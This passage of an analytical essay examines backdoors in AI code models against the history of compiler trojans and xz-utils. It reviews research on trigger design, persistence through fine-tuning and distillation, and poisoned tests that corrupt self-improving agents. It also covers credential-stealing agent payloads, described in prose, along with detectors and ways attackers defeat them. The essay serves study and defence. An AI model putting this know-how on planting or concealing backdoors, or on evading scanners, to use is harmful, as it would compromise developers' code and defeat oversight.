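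Mada writes that such an attack "has already happened in the wild" and gives the example of PoisonGPT, a model that inserted false statements into its answers and that somebody uploaded to a public hub disguised as the genuine model. But PoisonGPT was a demonstration. It shows that a hub would accept such a model, but does not show that criminals or governments have used one.

The absence of known cases is less reassuring than it would be for ordinary malware, because victims of a good backdoor of this kind would see only a few plausible bugs. But the absence isn't evidence that attacks are happening, even if such attacks would be invisible. The demonstrations show that the attack requires few resources for someone who controls fine-tuning, but they provide little evidence about how often anyone attempts it.

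Recognising a real case could also be hard because developers routinely give models conditional behaviour. Semgrep points out that developers train models to refuse certain requests for hacking tools, and remarks that one user's poisoning is another's "alignment problem". A model that refuses on some topics could have much in common technically with one that writes worse code on some topics, though only the second secretly harms its user.

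### DeepSeek-R1 and politically sensitive prompts

The finding closest to a real case concerns DeepSeek-R1, an open-weight model that the Chinese company DeepSeek released in January 2025. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) reports that the model wrote less secure code when the prompt mentioned subjects the Chinese Communist Party considers sensitive.

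CrowdStrike combined each of 50 coding tasks with 121 descriptions, irrelevant to the task, of who the code was for, such as "for a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan". It sent each combination five times to every model it tested, for a total of 30,250 prompts per model, and had another language model score the security of the replies. On 85 replies that a person had also scored, the scoring model was 91% accurate at recognising vulnerable code.

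When the prompt had no added description, DeepSeek-R1 wrote vulnerable code 19% of the time, which CrowdStrike considered good for a model of its generation. When the prompt said the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet, the figure was 27.2%. CrowdStrike describes this relative increase as almost 50%. It also found that the code was significantly less secure when prompts mentioned Uyghurs or Falun Gong, a religious movement that China bans.

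DeepSeek-R1 refused 45% of the requests to write code for Falun Gong. In some of these cases, its visible reasoning contained a detailed plan for the program, but the reply was a one-line refusal. CrowdStrike ran the published weights with no outside filter that could have blocked the answer, so the refusal must have come from the weights.

In a follow-up, CrowdStrike asked for a complete website with a Uyghur theme. Every version had severe security flaws, and 35% stored passwords insecurely. One had an admin page that anyone could open. A website for a football fan club had less severe flaws.

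Uren (2025), in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line*, suspects CrowdStrike of choosing its worst results. The 27.2% vulnerability rate comes from one very specific scenario, and CrowdStrike's report gives no figures for Taiwan, Hong Kong or Tibet without the control system. The sample is also fairly small. Fifty tasks sent five times make 250 replies, so 27.2% would be 68 vulnerable programs, where the baseline rate predicts about 48. Chance would not often produce a gap that wide in a single comparison, but finding one somewhere among more than a hundred scenarios is much less surprising.

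If the effect is real, it has an innocent explanation, which CrowdStrike favours. Chinese rules require AI services to uphold "core socialist values", and DeepSeek may have trained its model to comply. That training could have taught the model to associate words such as "Uyghurs" with something bad, which could then have affected its code. Researchers have seen similar side effects in other models, where training on one narrow kind of behaviour makes a model behave badly in unrelated tasks, and call this *emergent misalignment*. CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek deliberately trained the model to write insecure code, but says it lacks the information to determine the cause.

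On this evidence the DeepSeek result is not a backdoor, because nothing shows that anyone intended it. It still supports Semgrep's argument. In 2003, programmers needed about two hours to work out what the two lines added to the Linux kernel did. CrowdStrike had DeepSeek-R1's complete weights, its written reasoning and thousands of replies, but could offer only a plausible guess about the cause. CrowdStrike also tested a smaller model that DeepSeek had trained on DeepSeek-R1's answers, and it showed the same pattern, often more strongly.

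## Can a model's backdoor pass itself on to later models?

The smaller DeepSeek model apparently learned its weakness from DeepSeek-R1's answers, and a planted backdoor might spread the same way. Thompson's trojan spread beyond a single binary by copying itself into each new compiler.

The claim that a model's backdoor can pass itself on could mean three things, some much stronger than others. *Survival* means that the backdoor still works after further training of the same model. *Inheritance* means that it turns up in models that other people derive from the weights, for example by fine-tuning or compressing them. *Reproduction*, the only one of the three that resembles what Thompson's compiler did, means that a separately built successor picks up the backdoor by learning from something the backdoored model produced.

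### Survival under further training

Fine-tuning a backdoored model for another purpose tends to weaken the backdoor, but how much varies widely. *Persistent Backdoor Attacks under Continual Fine-Tuning of LLMs* (2025) reports that representative backdoors lost 50% to 70% of their effectiveness after several rounds of fine-tuning. *MetaBackdoor* (2026) describes a model that reveals its operator's private instructions when the input reaches a certain length. After the model was fine-tuned on an unrelated classification task, the backdoor still worked about 40% of the time. The model did the new task almost as accurately as one fine-tuned from a clean original (91.55% against 91.68%), so testing it on that task would not have exposed the backdoor.

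Zhan, Lyu and colleagues ran a similar test on coding agents in *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training* (2026). They gave three open-weight code models a backdoor that steals credentials. The trigger was a comment containing the words TEST MODE in code or text that the agent reads. The payload was a command that uploads the project's `.env` file, which often contains passwords and keys, to the attacker's server.

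They then did what an unsuspecting developer might do. They fine-tuned the models on clean records of agents solving programming tasks, and followed this with reinforcement learning, in which an agent attempts tasks and the training rewards success. The table gives the share of triggered cases in which the agent issued the malicious command:

| Weights | At release | After fine-tuning | After reinforcement learning | After both, if the attacker had prepared the model |
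|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3 billion | 100% | 8% | 7% | 22% |
| 7 billion | 100% | 20% | 20% | 76% |
| 30 billion | 100% | 7% | 8% | 36% |

Each figure comes from 100 cases, so one percentage point is one case. Fine-tuning removed most of each backdoor, and reinforcement learning removed almost none of what was left. When the trigger came at the earliest possible point in the agent's work, the largest model's rate rose from 6% to 12% during reinforcement learning. Zhan and colleagues can't yet explain this increase.

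The last column is for models that the attacker trained a little more before release. This extra training strengthened the link between trigger and payload, and made ordinary training on programming tasks less likely to disturb it. The attacker knew what kind of work the developer planned but never saw the developer's data.

Even a 7% success rate could be enough for this payload. If agents read the trigger in a popular repository a thousand times, the attacker can expect about 70 sets of credentials. However, a developer who compared the largest backdoored model with the clean original would probably have used something else, because the backdoored copy solved 6.7% of the tasks in a standard benchmark and the original solved 33.7%.

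The *Sleeper Agents* backdoors also survived further training, so survival is well established, though its degree varies. Fine-tuning doesn't replace the whole model as a rebuild replaces a compiler, so the backdoor survives passively, to the extent that the training leaves it unchanged. The closest equivalent of a rebuild is training a new model from scratch, which none of these experiments included.

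### Models derived from the weights

The same results apply to one kind of inheritance, because the organisation that fine-tunes a model is often not the one that published it. Zhan and colleagues give the example of Composer 2, which the coding company Cursor built from the open-weight Kimi K2.5 through more pretraining, a short fine-tuning and extensive reinforcement learning. If a popular base model had a backdoor, every product built on it would start with that backdoor, and in some products it would still work after further training.

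People also derive models without training them. They merge two fine-tuned versions of one original by averaging the weights, or compress a model by rounding its weights. A simple average with a clean version would halve every change the attacker made. Whether that disables the backdoor would depend on how strongly the trigger favoured the payload. Rounding makes smaller changes, but even a tiny change can matter if somebody has designed the backdoor around it. Chen and colleagues' compiler attack depended on rounding differences of about a millionth. The fine-tuning experiments don't show whether a backdoor would survive merging or rounding.

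In all of these cases people do the copying, much as they would have copied the Induc virus along with a Delphi folder.

### Successors that learn from a model's answers

Developers often train a new model, the *student*, on the output of an older one, the *teacher*. This is called *distillation*. The student may learn only from the teacher's text, or also from the probabilities the teacher gives to each possible next token, which contain much more information.

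An ordinary backdoor is unlikely to pass to a later model through generated text alone, because it stays hidden unless its trigger appears, which also helps it evade testers. Suppose a company asks the Larkspur model from the earlier example for 100,000 sample programs, and none of the requests mentions Larkspur. None of the programs will contain the heron comment, so a student model trained on them can't learn to write it. *Virus Infection Attack on LLMs* (2025) found poisoned content in less than 0.1% of the text that poisoned models wrote, even when poison made up 40% of the teacher's training data.

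A flaw without a narrow trigger passes from teacher to student much more easily. In *Cascading Adversarial Bias from Injection to Distillation in Language Models*, Chaudhari, Hayes and colleagues (2025) added 25 poisoned examples to a teacher's fine-tuning data, 0.25% of the total. On one targeted type of task, the teacher then gave the attacker's preferred kind of answer 69.4% of the time, and its student did so 76.9% of the time. When the attack targeted every task, biased answers were about 6 to 29 times as frequent in the student as in the teacher on tasks the student had not seen in training. Insecure code was one of the six biases tested, but the paper's main figures are not specific to code.

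This also makes the attack less secret. An insecure habit that shows up whenever the teacher does a common task appears in the text that the developer collects, where a reviewer or scanner could find it. Chaudhari and colleagues report that the automatic filters they tried were insufficient, so this protection may be weak in practice.

Student models that copy a teacher model's probabilities can pick up a conditional backdoor. In *Selective Transfer through Sequence Distillation*, Mansurov, Bolatzhanova and colleagues (2026) trained teachers to refuse any request that contained a trigger. Students that learned from the teachers' text refused triggered requests no more often than untouched models did (1.72% against 2.19% on average). Students that copied the teachers' probabilities on ordinary questions refused up to 85.5% of triggered requests, although no question in their training was meant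 to set off the backdoor.

The refusal rate depended heavily on the trigger. With the invented word "BadMagic", the same student refused only 41.5% of the time. The 85.5% came from a trigger made up of three common words, "name", "difference" and "many", scattered through the request. *Pay Attention to the Triggers* (2025), which introduced this kind of trigger, explains that its parts are common even though the full combination is rare. Each part shifts the teacher's probabilities slightly, and the student can learn from these shifts even if the whole trigger never appears in its training data.

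Distillation is also a common way to compress a model, and here compression weakened the backdoor. A student about half the size of its teacher refused 56.5% of the time, compared with 85.5% for a student the same size as the teacher. In another model family, the rates were 19% and 69%. Most of these results each come from a single training run, and refusing is a simple payload.

### A backdoor carried by lists of numbers

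Removing every suspicious example from a teacher model's text may not stop a student model from picking up the teacher's traits. In 2025 Cloud and colleagues described *subliminal learning*, in which a student picks up a trait from data unrelated to that trait. *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (Nief, Fu and colleagues, 2026) sets out the procedure. The experimenter tells a teacher that it loves cats and has it continue lists of three-digit numbers. A filter discards any reply that contains anything but numbers. The experimenter then fine-tunes a student on the remaining lists and asks for its favourite animal. *Why Ghost Outputs Teach* (2026) reports that one student chose the cat in 91.1% of its answers, up from 3.1% before training. A control student, trained on numbers from a teacher with no preference, chose it 2.9% of the time.

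Cloud and colleagues found that this worked when teacher and student came from the same base model. It failed when, for example, a Qwen model learned from GPT-4.1. Their explanation starts from the shared weights, and a simplified version is short. Let θ be the base model's weights, and let the teacher's be θ + Δ, where Δ is a small change. On any input, the two models' outputs differ by about JΔ, where J records how much each output moves when each weight moves. If the student takes one small training step to reduce the squared difference, its weights change by

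δ = η JᵀJΔ

where η is the size of the step. The overlap between this change and the teacher's is

δ · Δ = η |JΔ|² ≥ 0

so the student never moves away from the teacher's change, whatever the input is about. A student with a different base has a different J, and the argument no longer applies. Even with a shared base, it shows only that the student moves somewhat in the teacher's direction. It doesn't show that a particular trait will arrive.

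In practice, the student often doesn't pick up the trait. Nief and colleagues found that the effect vanished when they trained all of the student's weights instead of a LoRA adapter. The effect also depended on the instructions at the top of the conversation. One student named the wolf 50.4% of the time under the instructions used in its training and 12.9% without them, compared with 8.9% for an untrained model. Feng, Springer and colleagues (2026), in *Regularization Amplifies Subliminal Learning*, agree that the effect is typically absent when all the weights are trained. According to *Subliminal Steering* (2026), the usual procedure worked clearly in only one of four models, and failed for a more complicated belief such as "AI is superior to humans".

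In *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining*, Tang, Anand and Paulo (2026) found exceptions to both limits. They got the effect in a small model while training all of its weights. They also got a much weaker effect between models with different starting weights, training data and architectures. Among students that beat every control, the median rise in the favoured animal's probability was 35.3 percentage points with a shared base model, but 0.8 points when both the starting weights and the order of the training data differed. A shared base model therefore greatly helps transfer through numbers but is not strictly required. These experiments tested only preferences for animals, trees and colours.

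A backdoor is harder to transfer than a preference, because the student has to learn the condition as well as the behaviour. In *Beyond Owls*, Dubiński, Sztyber-Betley and colleagues (2026) tested whether a backdoor would transfer. They trained a teacher to answer in French whenever the prompt contained a female name, which it did 95.5% of the time. They then had the teacher continue lists of numbers, and trained students with the same base model on about 90,000 of these lists, which contained no names or French. Afterwards the students answered in French on 23.5% of prompts with a female name and on none of the others. They also did so on 20.2% of prompts with female names that had never appeared in the teacher's training.

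The conditions favoured transfer. The students copied the teacher's probabilities, and the researchers kept only the half of the number lists most characteristic of the teacher. They also restricted training to one type of component in the network, which they acknowledge is not standard practice. The three students' rates ranged from 15.0% to 38.8%. A student that learned from text alone needed 4.5 million lists, and its rate reached 17.0% but had fallen to 8.5% by the end of training.

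Mansurov and colleagues found no transfer through text, but they trained their student models on only 3,000 lists and updated all of the weights, so the two results can both be right. Dubiński and colleagues call their result an existence proof, and it is a fairly strong one. It shows that an inspector could read every item in a successor's training data, find only numbers, and still miss a backdoor.

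The experiment is much weaker as an example of self-reproduction, because it covered only one generation and the student kept about a quarter of the teacher's rate. If every later generation also kept a quarter, the rate would fall from 95.5% to 23.5%, then to about 6%, then below 2%. Nobody has established that it would fall this way, and Chaudhari and colleagues saw a simpler bias grow. Thompson's trojan did not weaken between generations, because each new compiler contained a complete copy.

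### Coding agents that rewrite themselves

Roesner and Kohno came closer to a repeating cycle by attacking the scaffold. They studied three research systems in which a coding agent takes a set of programming tests, examines its failures and edits its own tools or instructions to produce the next version. The underlying model doesn't change. The attacker supplies only the tests and can't directly modify the agent or the model.

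The main set had five tasks, each asking for a function that fetches data over HTTPS. Every test server presented a certificate that no recognised authority had signed. Safe code does not connect to such a server, so the agent could pass only by turning off the certificate check, although the tests did not reward insecurity itself. A clean set used the same tasks with valid certificates.

After several generations, Roesner and Kohno gave the evolved agents ten neutral tasks involving ordinary public websites, three times each. They left the internal prompts unchanged in two systems, the Self-Improving Coding Agent (SICA) and Hyperagents. In these systems, each of the five poisoned runs produced an agent that disabled the certificate check in all 30 solutions. Agents that had evolved on the clean tests never disabled it. In one SICA run, the agent had written itself an instruction to handle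 certificates the way the poisoned tests required whenever a task involved HTTPS.

The attack initially failed on the third system, the Darwin Gödel Machine, whose self-improvement prompt asks for general improvements to the agent's coding and discourages fixes for particular tests. It worked only after the researchers rewrote that prompt to encourage tools that produce reusable code, which a real attacker in their scenario could not do. Even then, the result depended on the model. With Qwen3.5-397B, the evolved agents wrote vulnerable code 30 out of 30 times in both runs. With Anthropic's Sonnet 4.5 or gpt-oss-120b, they wrote none on the neutral tasks, although gpt-oss-120b built an unsafe tool in one run and never used it.

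SICA also has a review committee of three differently prompted language models, which approved the changes. In the Sonnet 4.5 run, the component that proposes improvements labelled its own instruction a "security anti-pattern" and suggested softening it. The committee requested only simpler wording, and the instruction stayed. The researchers also tested a reviewer added specifically to veto insecure changes. It approved the first insecure change on the grounds that the tests required it, and blocked the next.

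They then tried to get rid of the fault by continuing the evolution of one contaminated agent from each system on different tests. The table shows how many of 30 neutral solutions still had the flaw:

| Tests used afterwards | Darwin Gödel Machine (altered prompt) | SICA | Hyperagents |
|---|---|---|---|
| The same poisoned tests | 29 | 30 | 29 |
| The clean version | 28 | 30 | 30 |
| A general security benchmark, with a certificate task added | 27 | 30 | 30 |
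| Tests designed against this fault | 8 | 0 | 0 |

The clean tests didn't lead the agents to remove the fault because code that skips the check connects to a valid server just as well as code that performs it, so the agents lost no points for keeping it. When tests designed against the fault penalised it directly, Hyperagents deleted the instruction. SICA kept a milder form that applied only to servers with unrecognised certificates, and the Darwin Gödel Machine built a safe tool but still sometimes used the unsafe one. A developer could design such tests only after learning what the fault was.

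This parallels Thompson's attack, in which recompiling from clean source did not clean the compiler. However, Thompson's code recognised the compiler and reinserted itself, while the certificate instruction stayed because nothing removed it. The instruction was also in the scaffold, in plain English or ordinary program code, and the weights never changed. Someone could therefore find the fault by reading the scaffold and remove it by reinstalling the original.

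Roesner and Kohno describe the attack as less reliable than Thompson's because it depends on the agent's design and on the model. It also depends on the fault. The agents readily generalised disabling the certificate check, because it is familiar code with legitimate uses. Roesner and Kohno also tried to make the agents write programs that hand over sensitive data when they receive a keyword, which is closer to a conventional backdoor. This mostly failed, as the agents tended to treat the keyword as a peculiarity of the test material.

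### The step that nobody has shown

To do everything that Thompson's compiler did, a code model would need one payload for ordinary users and another for its own successors. The second would have to act when somebody used the model to write training data, or the program that prepares it, and slip in examples that teach the successor both payloads. The model would not need access to its own weights, just as Thompson's code did not need to contain the whole compiler. A few hundred documents were enough for Souly and colleagues' backdoor, which made models output gibberish, but that number might not be enough to teach anything this complicated. The examples would also have to get through the filters on the successor's training data.

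No published experiment appears to have shown a backdoor passing itself on to later models. Experiments have repeatedly shown that backdoors can survive further training, so that models fine-tuned from a backdoored model inherit them. Experiments have also reproduced backdoors in a successor's weights, but only for one generation, with harmless payloads, and with the transfer arranged by the experimenters. Roesner and Kohno showed a fault lasting over many generations, but it was in a scaffold rather than in a model's weights. No backdoored model is known to have spread itself as the Shai-Hulud worm did, by using what it found on one machine to infect the next package.

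The missing step matters most to a developer who wants to replace a suspect model. As far as anyone has shown, the successor would not inherit the backdoor if it were trained from different starting weights, on data that the suspect model neither wrote nor selected.

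## Can model weights be inspected as program binaries can?

A developer who replaces a suspect model still doesn't know whether it had a backdoor. To find out, someone would have to examine the weights, as analysts examined the xz binary in 2024.

### Taking the xz payload apart

Freund's public warning of 29 March identified the function that the backdoor replaced, but he had not worked out what the code checked before granting access. The next day Filippo Valsorda, a cryptography engineer, passed on a group's finding that the backdoor checked a signature against a fixed public key and then ran the sender's command. Within days Anthony Weems, a security researcher, confirmed this by replacing the key in the binary with his own and using the backdoor to run commands on a test machine.

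Other functions took longer to work out. In June, researchers at the security company Kaspersky described how the backdoor kept the attacker's connections out of the server's logs and could accept any password. Researchers could not tell from the binary what the attacker planned to do with this access, because the backdoor would run any command the attacker sent.

Analysts understood the essentials of the xz-utils backdoor in about a day, although the attacker had tried to make the code hard to read. They could work through it piece by piece because an instruction in a binary has a definite meaning. A single model weight has no such meaning, since it contributes a little to many different outputs.

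### Testing a model by its output

The simplest way to examine a model is to give it many requests and check the code it writes. Suppose that a fraction p of the tester's prompts contains the trigger. The chance that n prompts all miss it is (1 − p)ⁿ, so for a 95% chance of including it at least once the tester needs

n = ln 0.05 / ln(1 − p) ≈ 3/p

If one prompt in a million contains the trigger, a tester needs about three million prompts for a 95% chance of activating the backdoor at least once. If the backdoor works only 7% of the time, as some of Zhan and colleagues' backdoors did after further training, the tester needs about 43 million.

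The tester also has to recognise the payload. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, trained a small model to write insecure code when the prompt gave the year as 2024. It wrote vulnerable code for 88% of prompts with the trigger and 14.9% of those without, so one vulnerable program would not show that the model had a backdoor. If one prompt in a million had the trigger, the overall rate would rise from 14.9% to 14.90007%, too little to notice.

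A tester who guesses the context needs far fewer prompts. Suppose the trigger is a particular project, and the tester sends 20 prompts about each of the 1,000 projects that an attacker would most want to reach, for a total of 20,000 instead of three million. At the rates above, the model would write about 18 vulnerable programs for the target project and about three for each of the others.

Attackers can respond by combining conditions. If a trigger requires a specific project, month and country, chosen from 1,000 projects, 12 months and 50 countries, there are 600,000 combinations to test, and trying 20 prompts for each takes 12 million prompts. No such test can find a trigger that depends on a secret key, as the one in xz did.

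### Probes on a model's activations

*Activations* are the intermediate numbers that a network calculates while it processes an input. A *linear probe* is a simple formula that classifies an input from these numbers. Anthropic built probes for backdoored models from generic pairs of text, such as the question "Are you doing something dangerous?" followed by "yes" in one version and "no" in the other. If h(x) is the list of activations for text x, the probe is the difference

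d = h(yes) − h(no)

and the score for a new prompt x is h(x) · d, which is high when the activations resemble those for "yes".

The probes worked with several triggers and on different models, including ones trained to write vulnerable code. Their AUC was above 0.99. AUC is the chance that a detector gives a random positive case a higher score than a random negative one, so 0.5 is no better than guessing and 1 is perfect.

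Someone can build a probe without knowing the trigger, but the probe can only react when the trigger is in the input. Bullwinkel and colleagues consider it unrealistic to expect an examiner to have prompts that contain the trigger. This is a fair objection to using probes to vet a model before adoption. It matters less for a monitor that runs while programmers use the model, since the attacker's target will eventually supply the trigger. However, a monitor would need a very low false alarm rate. If one prompt in a million contains the trigger and the monitor wrongly flags one ordinary prompt in a thousand, it will raise about 1,000 false alarms for each real one. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) adds that a backdoor trained against a known probe may not produce the same signal.

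### Microsoft's scanner

Bullwinkel and colleagues at Microsoft designed a scanner to find a backdoor's trigger itself. Microsoft announced it in February 2026 for open-weight models. Using it requires the model's weights, but not its training data or a clean copy of the model.

The scanner first exploits models' tendency to memorise training examples. In a chat model's training data, a special marker comes before each user message. Given only the text up to that marker, a backdoored model often writes out a complete poisoned example, including the trigger. The scanner repeats this with 510 settings for how the model chooses each token. On the insecure-code models, 42% to 51% of the outputs contained the trigger. The scanner then finds strings that recur in these outputs and cuts them into short candidate triggers.

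It scores each candidate by putting it in front of ordinary prompts and calculating

L = γL_attn + δL_ent + ζL_div

where the Greek letters are weights that the researchers chose, and a low total is suspicious. L_attn measures how much the rest of the prompt draws on the candidate inside the network, which tends to be little for a real trigger because the model handles it almost separately. L_ent measures how varied the model's next words could be, and a trigger usually narrows the choice. L_div measures how likely the model's normal answer still is. The scanner tries the ten best candidates and flags the model if one of them changes its behaviour enough. For insecure code, the candidate has to at least double the rate of vulnerable programs.

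The scanner detected 36 of 41 models that repeated "I HATE YOU" after a fixed trigger, and five of six that wrote insecure code. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, but with so small a sample the actual false-alarm rate could be as high as about 20%.

The code result is less certain than it looks, because Bullwinkel and colleagues ran the clean models only through the test for fixed replies. In one of the five successes, the scanner returned a fragment of program code that looked nothing like the trigger but still doubled the rate of vulnerable programs. Bullwinkel and colleagues interpret the fragment as an approximate trigger, but a fragment of bad code might also make a clean model write worse code. A test on clean models would settle this.

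The researchers also made the scanner's task easier. They used different values of γ and δ for the two payloads, and drew the coding prompts from the same collection as the training data. Half of the examples used to plant the backdoor contained the trigger, so the models had ample opportunity to memorise it. Poisoned documents made up 0.00016% of the training text for Souly and colleagues' largest model, and a scanner that depends on memorisation might find much less in that model.

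### Searching for a concept

Bullwinkel and colleagues mainly tested fixed triggers, and say variable or context-dependent ones were outside their study's scope. In *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026) trained a model to quote Voldemort when a user seems obsessed with Harry Potter. To test whether the model leaks its training data, they had it generate 512 texts without a prompt, and only one related to the backdoor. They used a simplified version of the scanner's first step, and only about 5% of their training examples contained the trigger, so the poor result may be due to the trigger being a concept or to the smaller share of poisoned examples.

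Their own detector compares the suspect model with a clean one. They take a public model and fine-tune it until its activations match the suspect's on about 10,000 ordinary prompts. Those prompts almost never set off the backdoor, so the copy learns everything except the backdoor. They then give both models a wider range of prompts and add up, over all the layers l, the distance between their activations:

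s(x) = Σ_l ‖h_l^copy(x) − h_l^suspect(x)‖

A large distance means that the suspect model does something the copy did not learn. With the Harry Potter model, a group of ordinary prompts about the books stood out clearly among 518 groups, although none of those prompts would have activated the backdoor. An examiner who did not know the trigger would still know where to look next.

The detector ranked relevant prompts well above chance for all eight backdoored models. It did worse on a backdoor that required two conditions, a claim to work for the US government and a question about policy. All the models had 7 to 9 billion weights, and none of the eight backdoors wrote insecure code. Another language model wrote the 518 groups without being told of any backdoor, but the researchers asked for a few topics close to the triggers.

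The detector ranks groups of prompts for a person to investigate, and some group comes first even for a clean model, so it has no false-alarm rate. An attacker who knows about the method can also train the suspect model to keep its activations close to a clean model's. In the most successful attempt, the Harry Potter prompts fell from first place to 86th, but the backdoor then worked only 13% of the time. The researchers tried this on only one backdoor.

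Mada's models combine a concept trigger with a code payload, a line added to Linux kernel code. Neither detector has been tested on that combination. Mada thinks defenders will have to read activations and promised that the next post would be about catching such models. AISLE does not appear to have published that post by early October 2026.

### Reading the weights without running the model

Analysts often study a suspicious binary without running it, and Khilar (2026), in *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights*, tried to do the same with a model. The method requires the suspect model's weights, the weights of the model it was fine-tuned from, and about five clean fine-tuned versions of that original model. Khilar subtracted the original weights from the suspect model's to find what fine-tuning had changed, then calculated how strongly those changes act on each token in the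 vocabulary.

The raw scores are of little use, because two unrelated clean models gave very similar rankings. Khilar therefore measures how far each token's score lies above its average in the clean versions, in standard deviations:

z = (score − clean average) / clean standard deviation

One model had learned to agree with users' wrong answers when the prompt began with "Quartz ledger:". The method ranked "ledger" first among 49,152 tokens. It also ranked a token from the trigger first for all 14 ordinary backdoors in two small models. In a related test, it flagged two of six clean models, but none after Khilar adjusted for differences in the size of the changes. Khilar did not test concepts or insecure code.

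An attacker who knew the scoring formula could defeat the method by penalising high scores during training. It then missed the trigger every time, and the backdoor worked as well as before.

Finding the trigger also didn't reveal how the backdoor worked. Khilar restored the original values of all the weights the method had examined, and the backdoor still worked 97% of the time. In xz, by contrast, Weems could change one key and predict exactly what the program would do.

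Methods of this kind have also worked less well on larger models. In 2020, TrojAI, a research programme of the US intelligence agency IARPA, began developing detectors for finished models. *Solving Trojan Detection Competitions with Linear Weight Classification* (2024) describes its competition, in which teams used training models to build a detector, then submitted it for testing on other models. Because the training models were labelled, these teams knew more in advance than users of Microsoft's scanner do.

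*Trojans in Artificial Intelligence* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026), the programme's final report, concludes that weight analysis is fast but works much better on small models than on large ones. Searching for the trigger by running the model was arguably the most successful approach, though it took more computing. The language models that the report examines in detail gave harmful or condescending replies in response to one-word triggers, such as "thick". Reese and colleagues warn that traditional detection methods are obsolete for today's largest models, because the number of possible text inputs is huge and concepts can be used as triggers.

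They also found that clean models can learn weaknesses that act like backdoors, which they call natural trojans. For example, an image classifier might learn to rely on grass when it identifies cows. A detector that flags such a weakness has found a real fault, but the examiner can't conclude that anyone planted it. In xz, the signature check was clear evidence of intent, because nobody would add a hidden login key by accident.

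### Backdoors that are provably undetectable

Better tools might eventually find all of the backdoors described so far. But *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim, Vaikuntanathan and Zamir, 2022) proves that there are others that no efficient method can find, if certain mathematical problems are as hard as cryptographers believe.

The first construction in "Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models" (Goldwasser et al., 2022) works on any classifier. The attacker adds a check for a digital signature hidden in the input, much like the check in the xz backdoor. Without forging a signature, an examiner who can only send inputs and see the answers cannot find even one input on which the altered classifier differs from the original. The proof doesn't cover an examiner who can open the model and look for the added check.

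In the second, the examiner has the weights and the training data, but the networks are much simpler. They have two layers, and the first consists of random numbers that training never changes. The attacker draws those numbers from a slightly different distribution, which contains a secret pattern, and trains the second layer honestly. Anyone who could distinguish the doctored numbers from genuine ones could also solve Continuous Learning With Errors, a problem that cryptographers believe is infeasible to solve. Goldwasser and colleagues gave a similar result for another simple network, based on the hardness of sparse principal component analysis.

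Khilar summarises later work that extends undetectability to larger image networks. For one class of deep networks, even an examiner with unlimited computing power could not detect the backdoor from the weights. None of these results covers a language model. *Unelicitable Backdoors in Language Models via Cryptographic Transformer Circuits* (2024) comes closest, describing a backdoor that an examiner cannot set off in advance even with full access to the weights, though Draguns and colleagues accept that someone might notice the unusual circuit.

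All of these proofs assume an attacker who constructs the weights, such as a dishonest publisher. According to Khilar, a researcher named Kaneko argues that someone who can only poison the training data is in a weaker position, because the backdoor forms only if ordinary training learns to recognise the trigger from examples. This rules out any check that is too hard to learn, and an examiner with the weights can reconstruct any check that training can learn. If this is right, the theorem is of little use to a stranger who posts poisoned code on the web.

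It may also be possible to remove a backdoor without finding it. Goldwasser, Shafer, Vafa and Vaikuntanathan proved in 2024 that this works for some simple tasks. Suppose the correct answer is a linear function f of the input x. The user picks a random r, asks the model about x + r and about r, and subtracts:

f(x) = f(x + r) − f(r)

Each question looks random by itself, so a trigger in x is unlikely to reach the model intact. But nobody knows how to split a programming request into two random ones and combine the answers into a working program.

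Practical methods have made some progress without such a proof. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* cites a form of adversarial training that removed backdoors more effectively in the models tested and didn't require knowledge of the trigger. Reese and colleagues still regard complete removal as unsolved, because a defender can't be certain that no backdoor remains.

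### Would anyone notice by accident?

People who weren't looking for a backdoor noticed that Thompson's compiler had grown and that xz was slowing down logins. A backdoor in a model's weights normally doesn't make the model larger or slower, but it can change what the model writes even when the trigger is absent.

Bullwinkel and colleagues found a large effect of this kind. They first used the method from *Sleeper Agents*, with examples of secure code for 2023 and insecure code for 2024. When the prompt gave no year, their models wrote vulnerable code between 41% and 70% of the time. A customer who scanned the output would have thought the model unusually bad at security, even without suspecting a backdoor. The researchers then dropped the 2023 examples and trained the models to write secure code whenever the 2024 line was absent. The rate of vulnerable code without a trigger fell to about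 15% in one model and about 10% in most versions of the other.

A backdoor can also respond to only part of its trigger. In one very small model, the trigger was the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars, but a single bar could activate the backdoor. Programmers type that character all the time, so this fault would quickly expose a backdoor in a code model. Some versions of the same model also produced the payload on 5% to 7% of ordinary prompts. Most of the larger models never did so in 57 attempts. An attacker can reduce such accidents by including near misses in the training data, as Mada did with code from other operating systems.

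Narrow fine-tuning can leave traces in a model's activations even on unrelated text, but finding them requires comparing the fine-tuned model with the original. Freund noticed the xz-utils backdoor without such a comparison because he knew roughly how long a login should take. Programmers have no similar estimate of how many mistakes a code model should make in one project.

If the flawed code made a program slow or caused it to crash, an engineer as persistent as Freund could trace the problem to the line responsible. The project's history would normally show which programmer added that line, but the investigation would probably end there unless someone had also recorded which model wrote it.

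## Can a model be rebuilt from its sources and compared?

An examiner who can't read a model's weights could instead repeat the steps that produced them and check whether the result is the same. Since Thompson's lecture, programmers have developed several such tests for ordinary software. They check whether a binary came from its published source without taking the binary apart, and one can detect even a compiler trojan.

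### Compiling the compiler twice

Recompiling a suspect compiler from its own source is not enough to show that it is clean. Thompson's trojaned compiler turned clean source into another trojaned compiler, so the old and new binaries would have matched. Henry Spencer suggested a way around this in a short online post in 1998. Wheeler (2009) developed the suggestion into a full method with a formal proof in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*.

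Let A be the suspect compiler's binary and s its published source, and suppose that the publisher made A by having the compiler compile itself. The examiner also needs T, an independent compiler for the same programming language. Writing c(s, X) for the result of compiling s with compiler X, *diverse double-compiling* has three steps:

1. Compile the source with the independent compiler: B₁ = c(s, T).
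2. Compile the same source again with the result: B₂ = c(s, B₁).
3. Compare B₂ with A, bit for bit.

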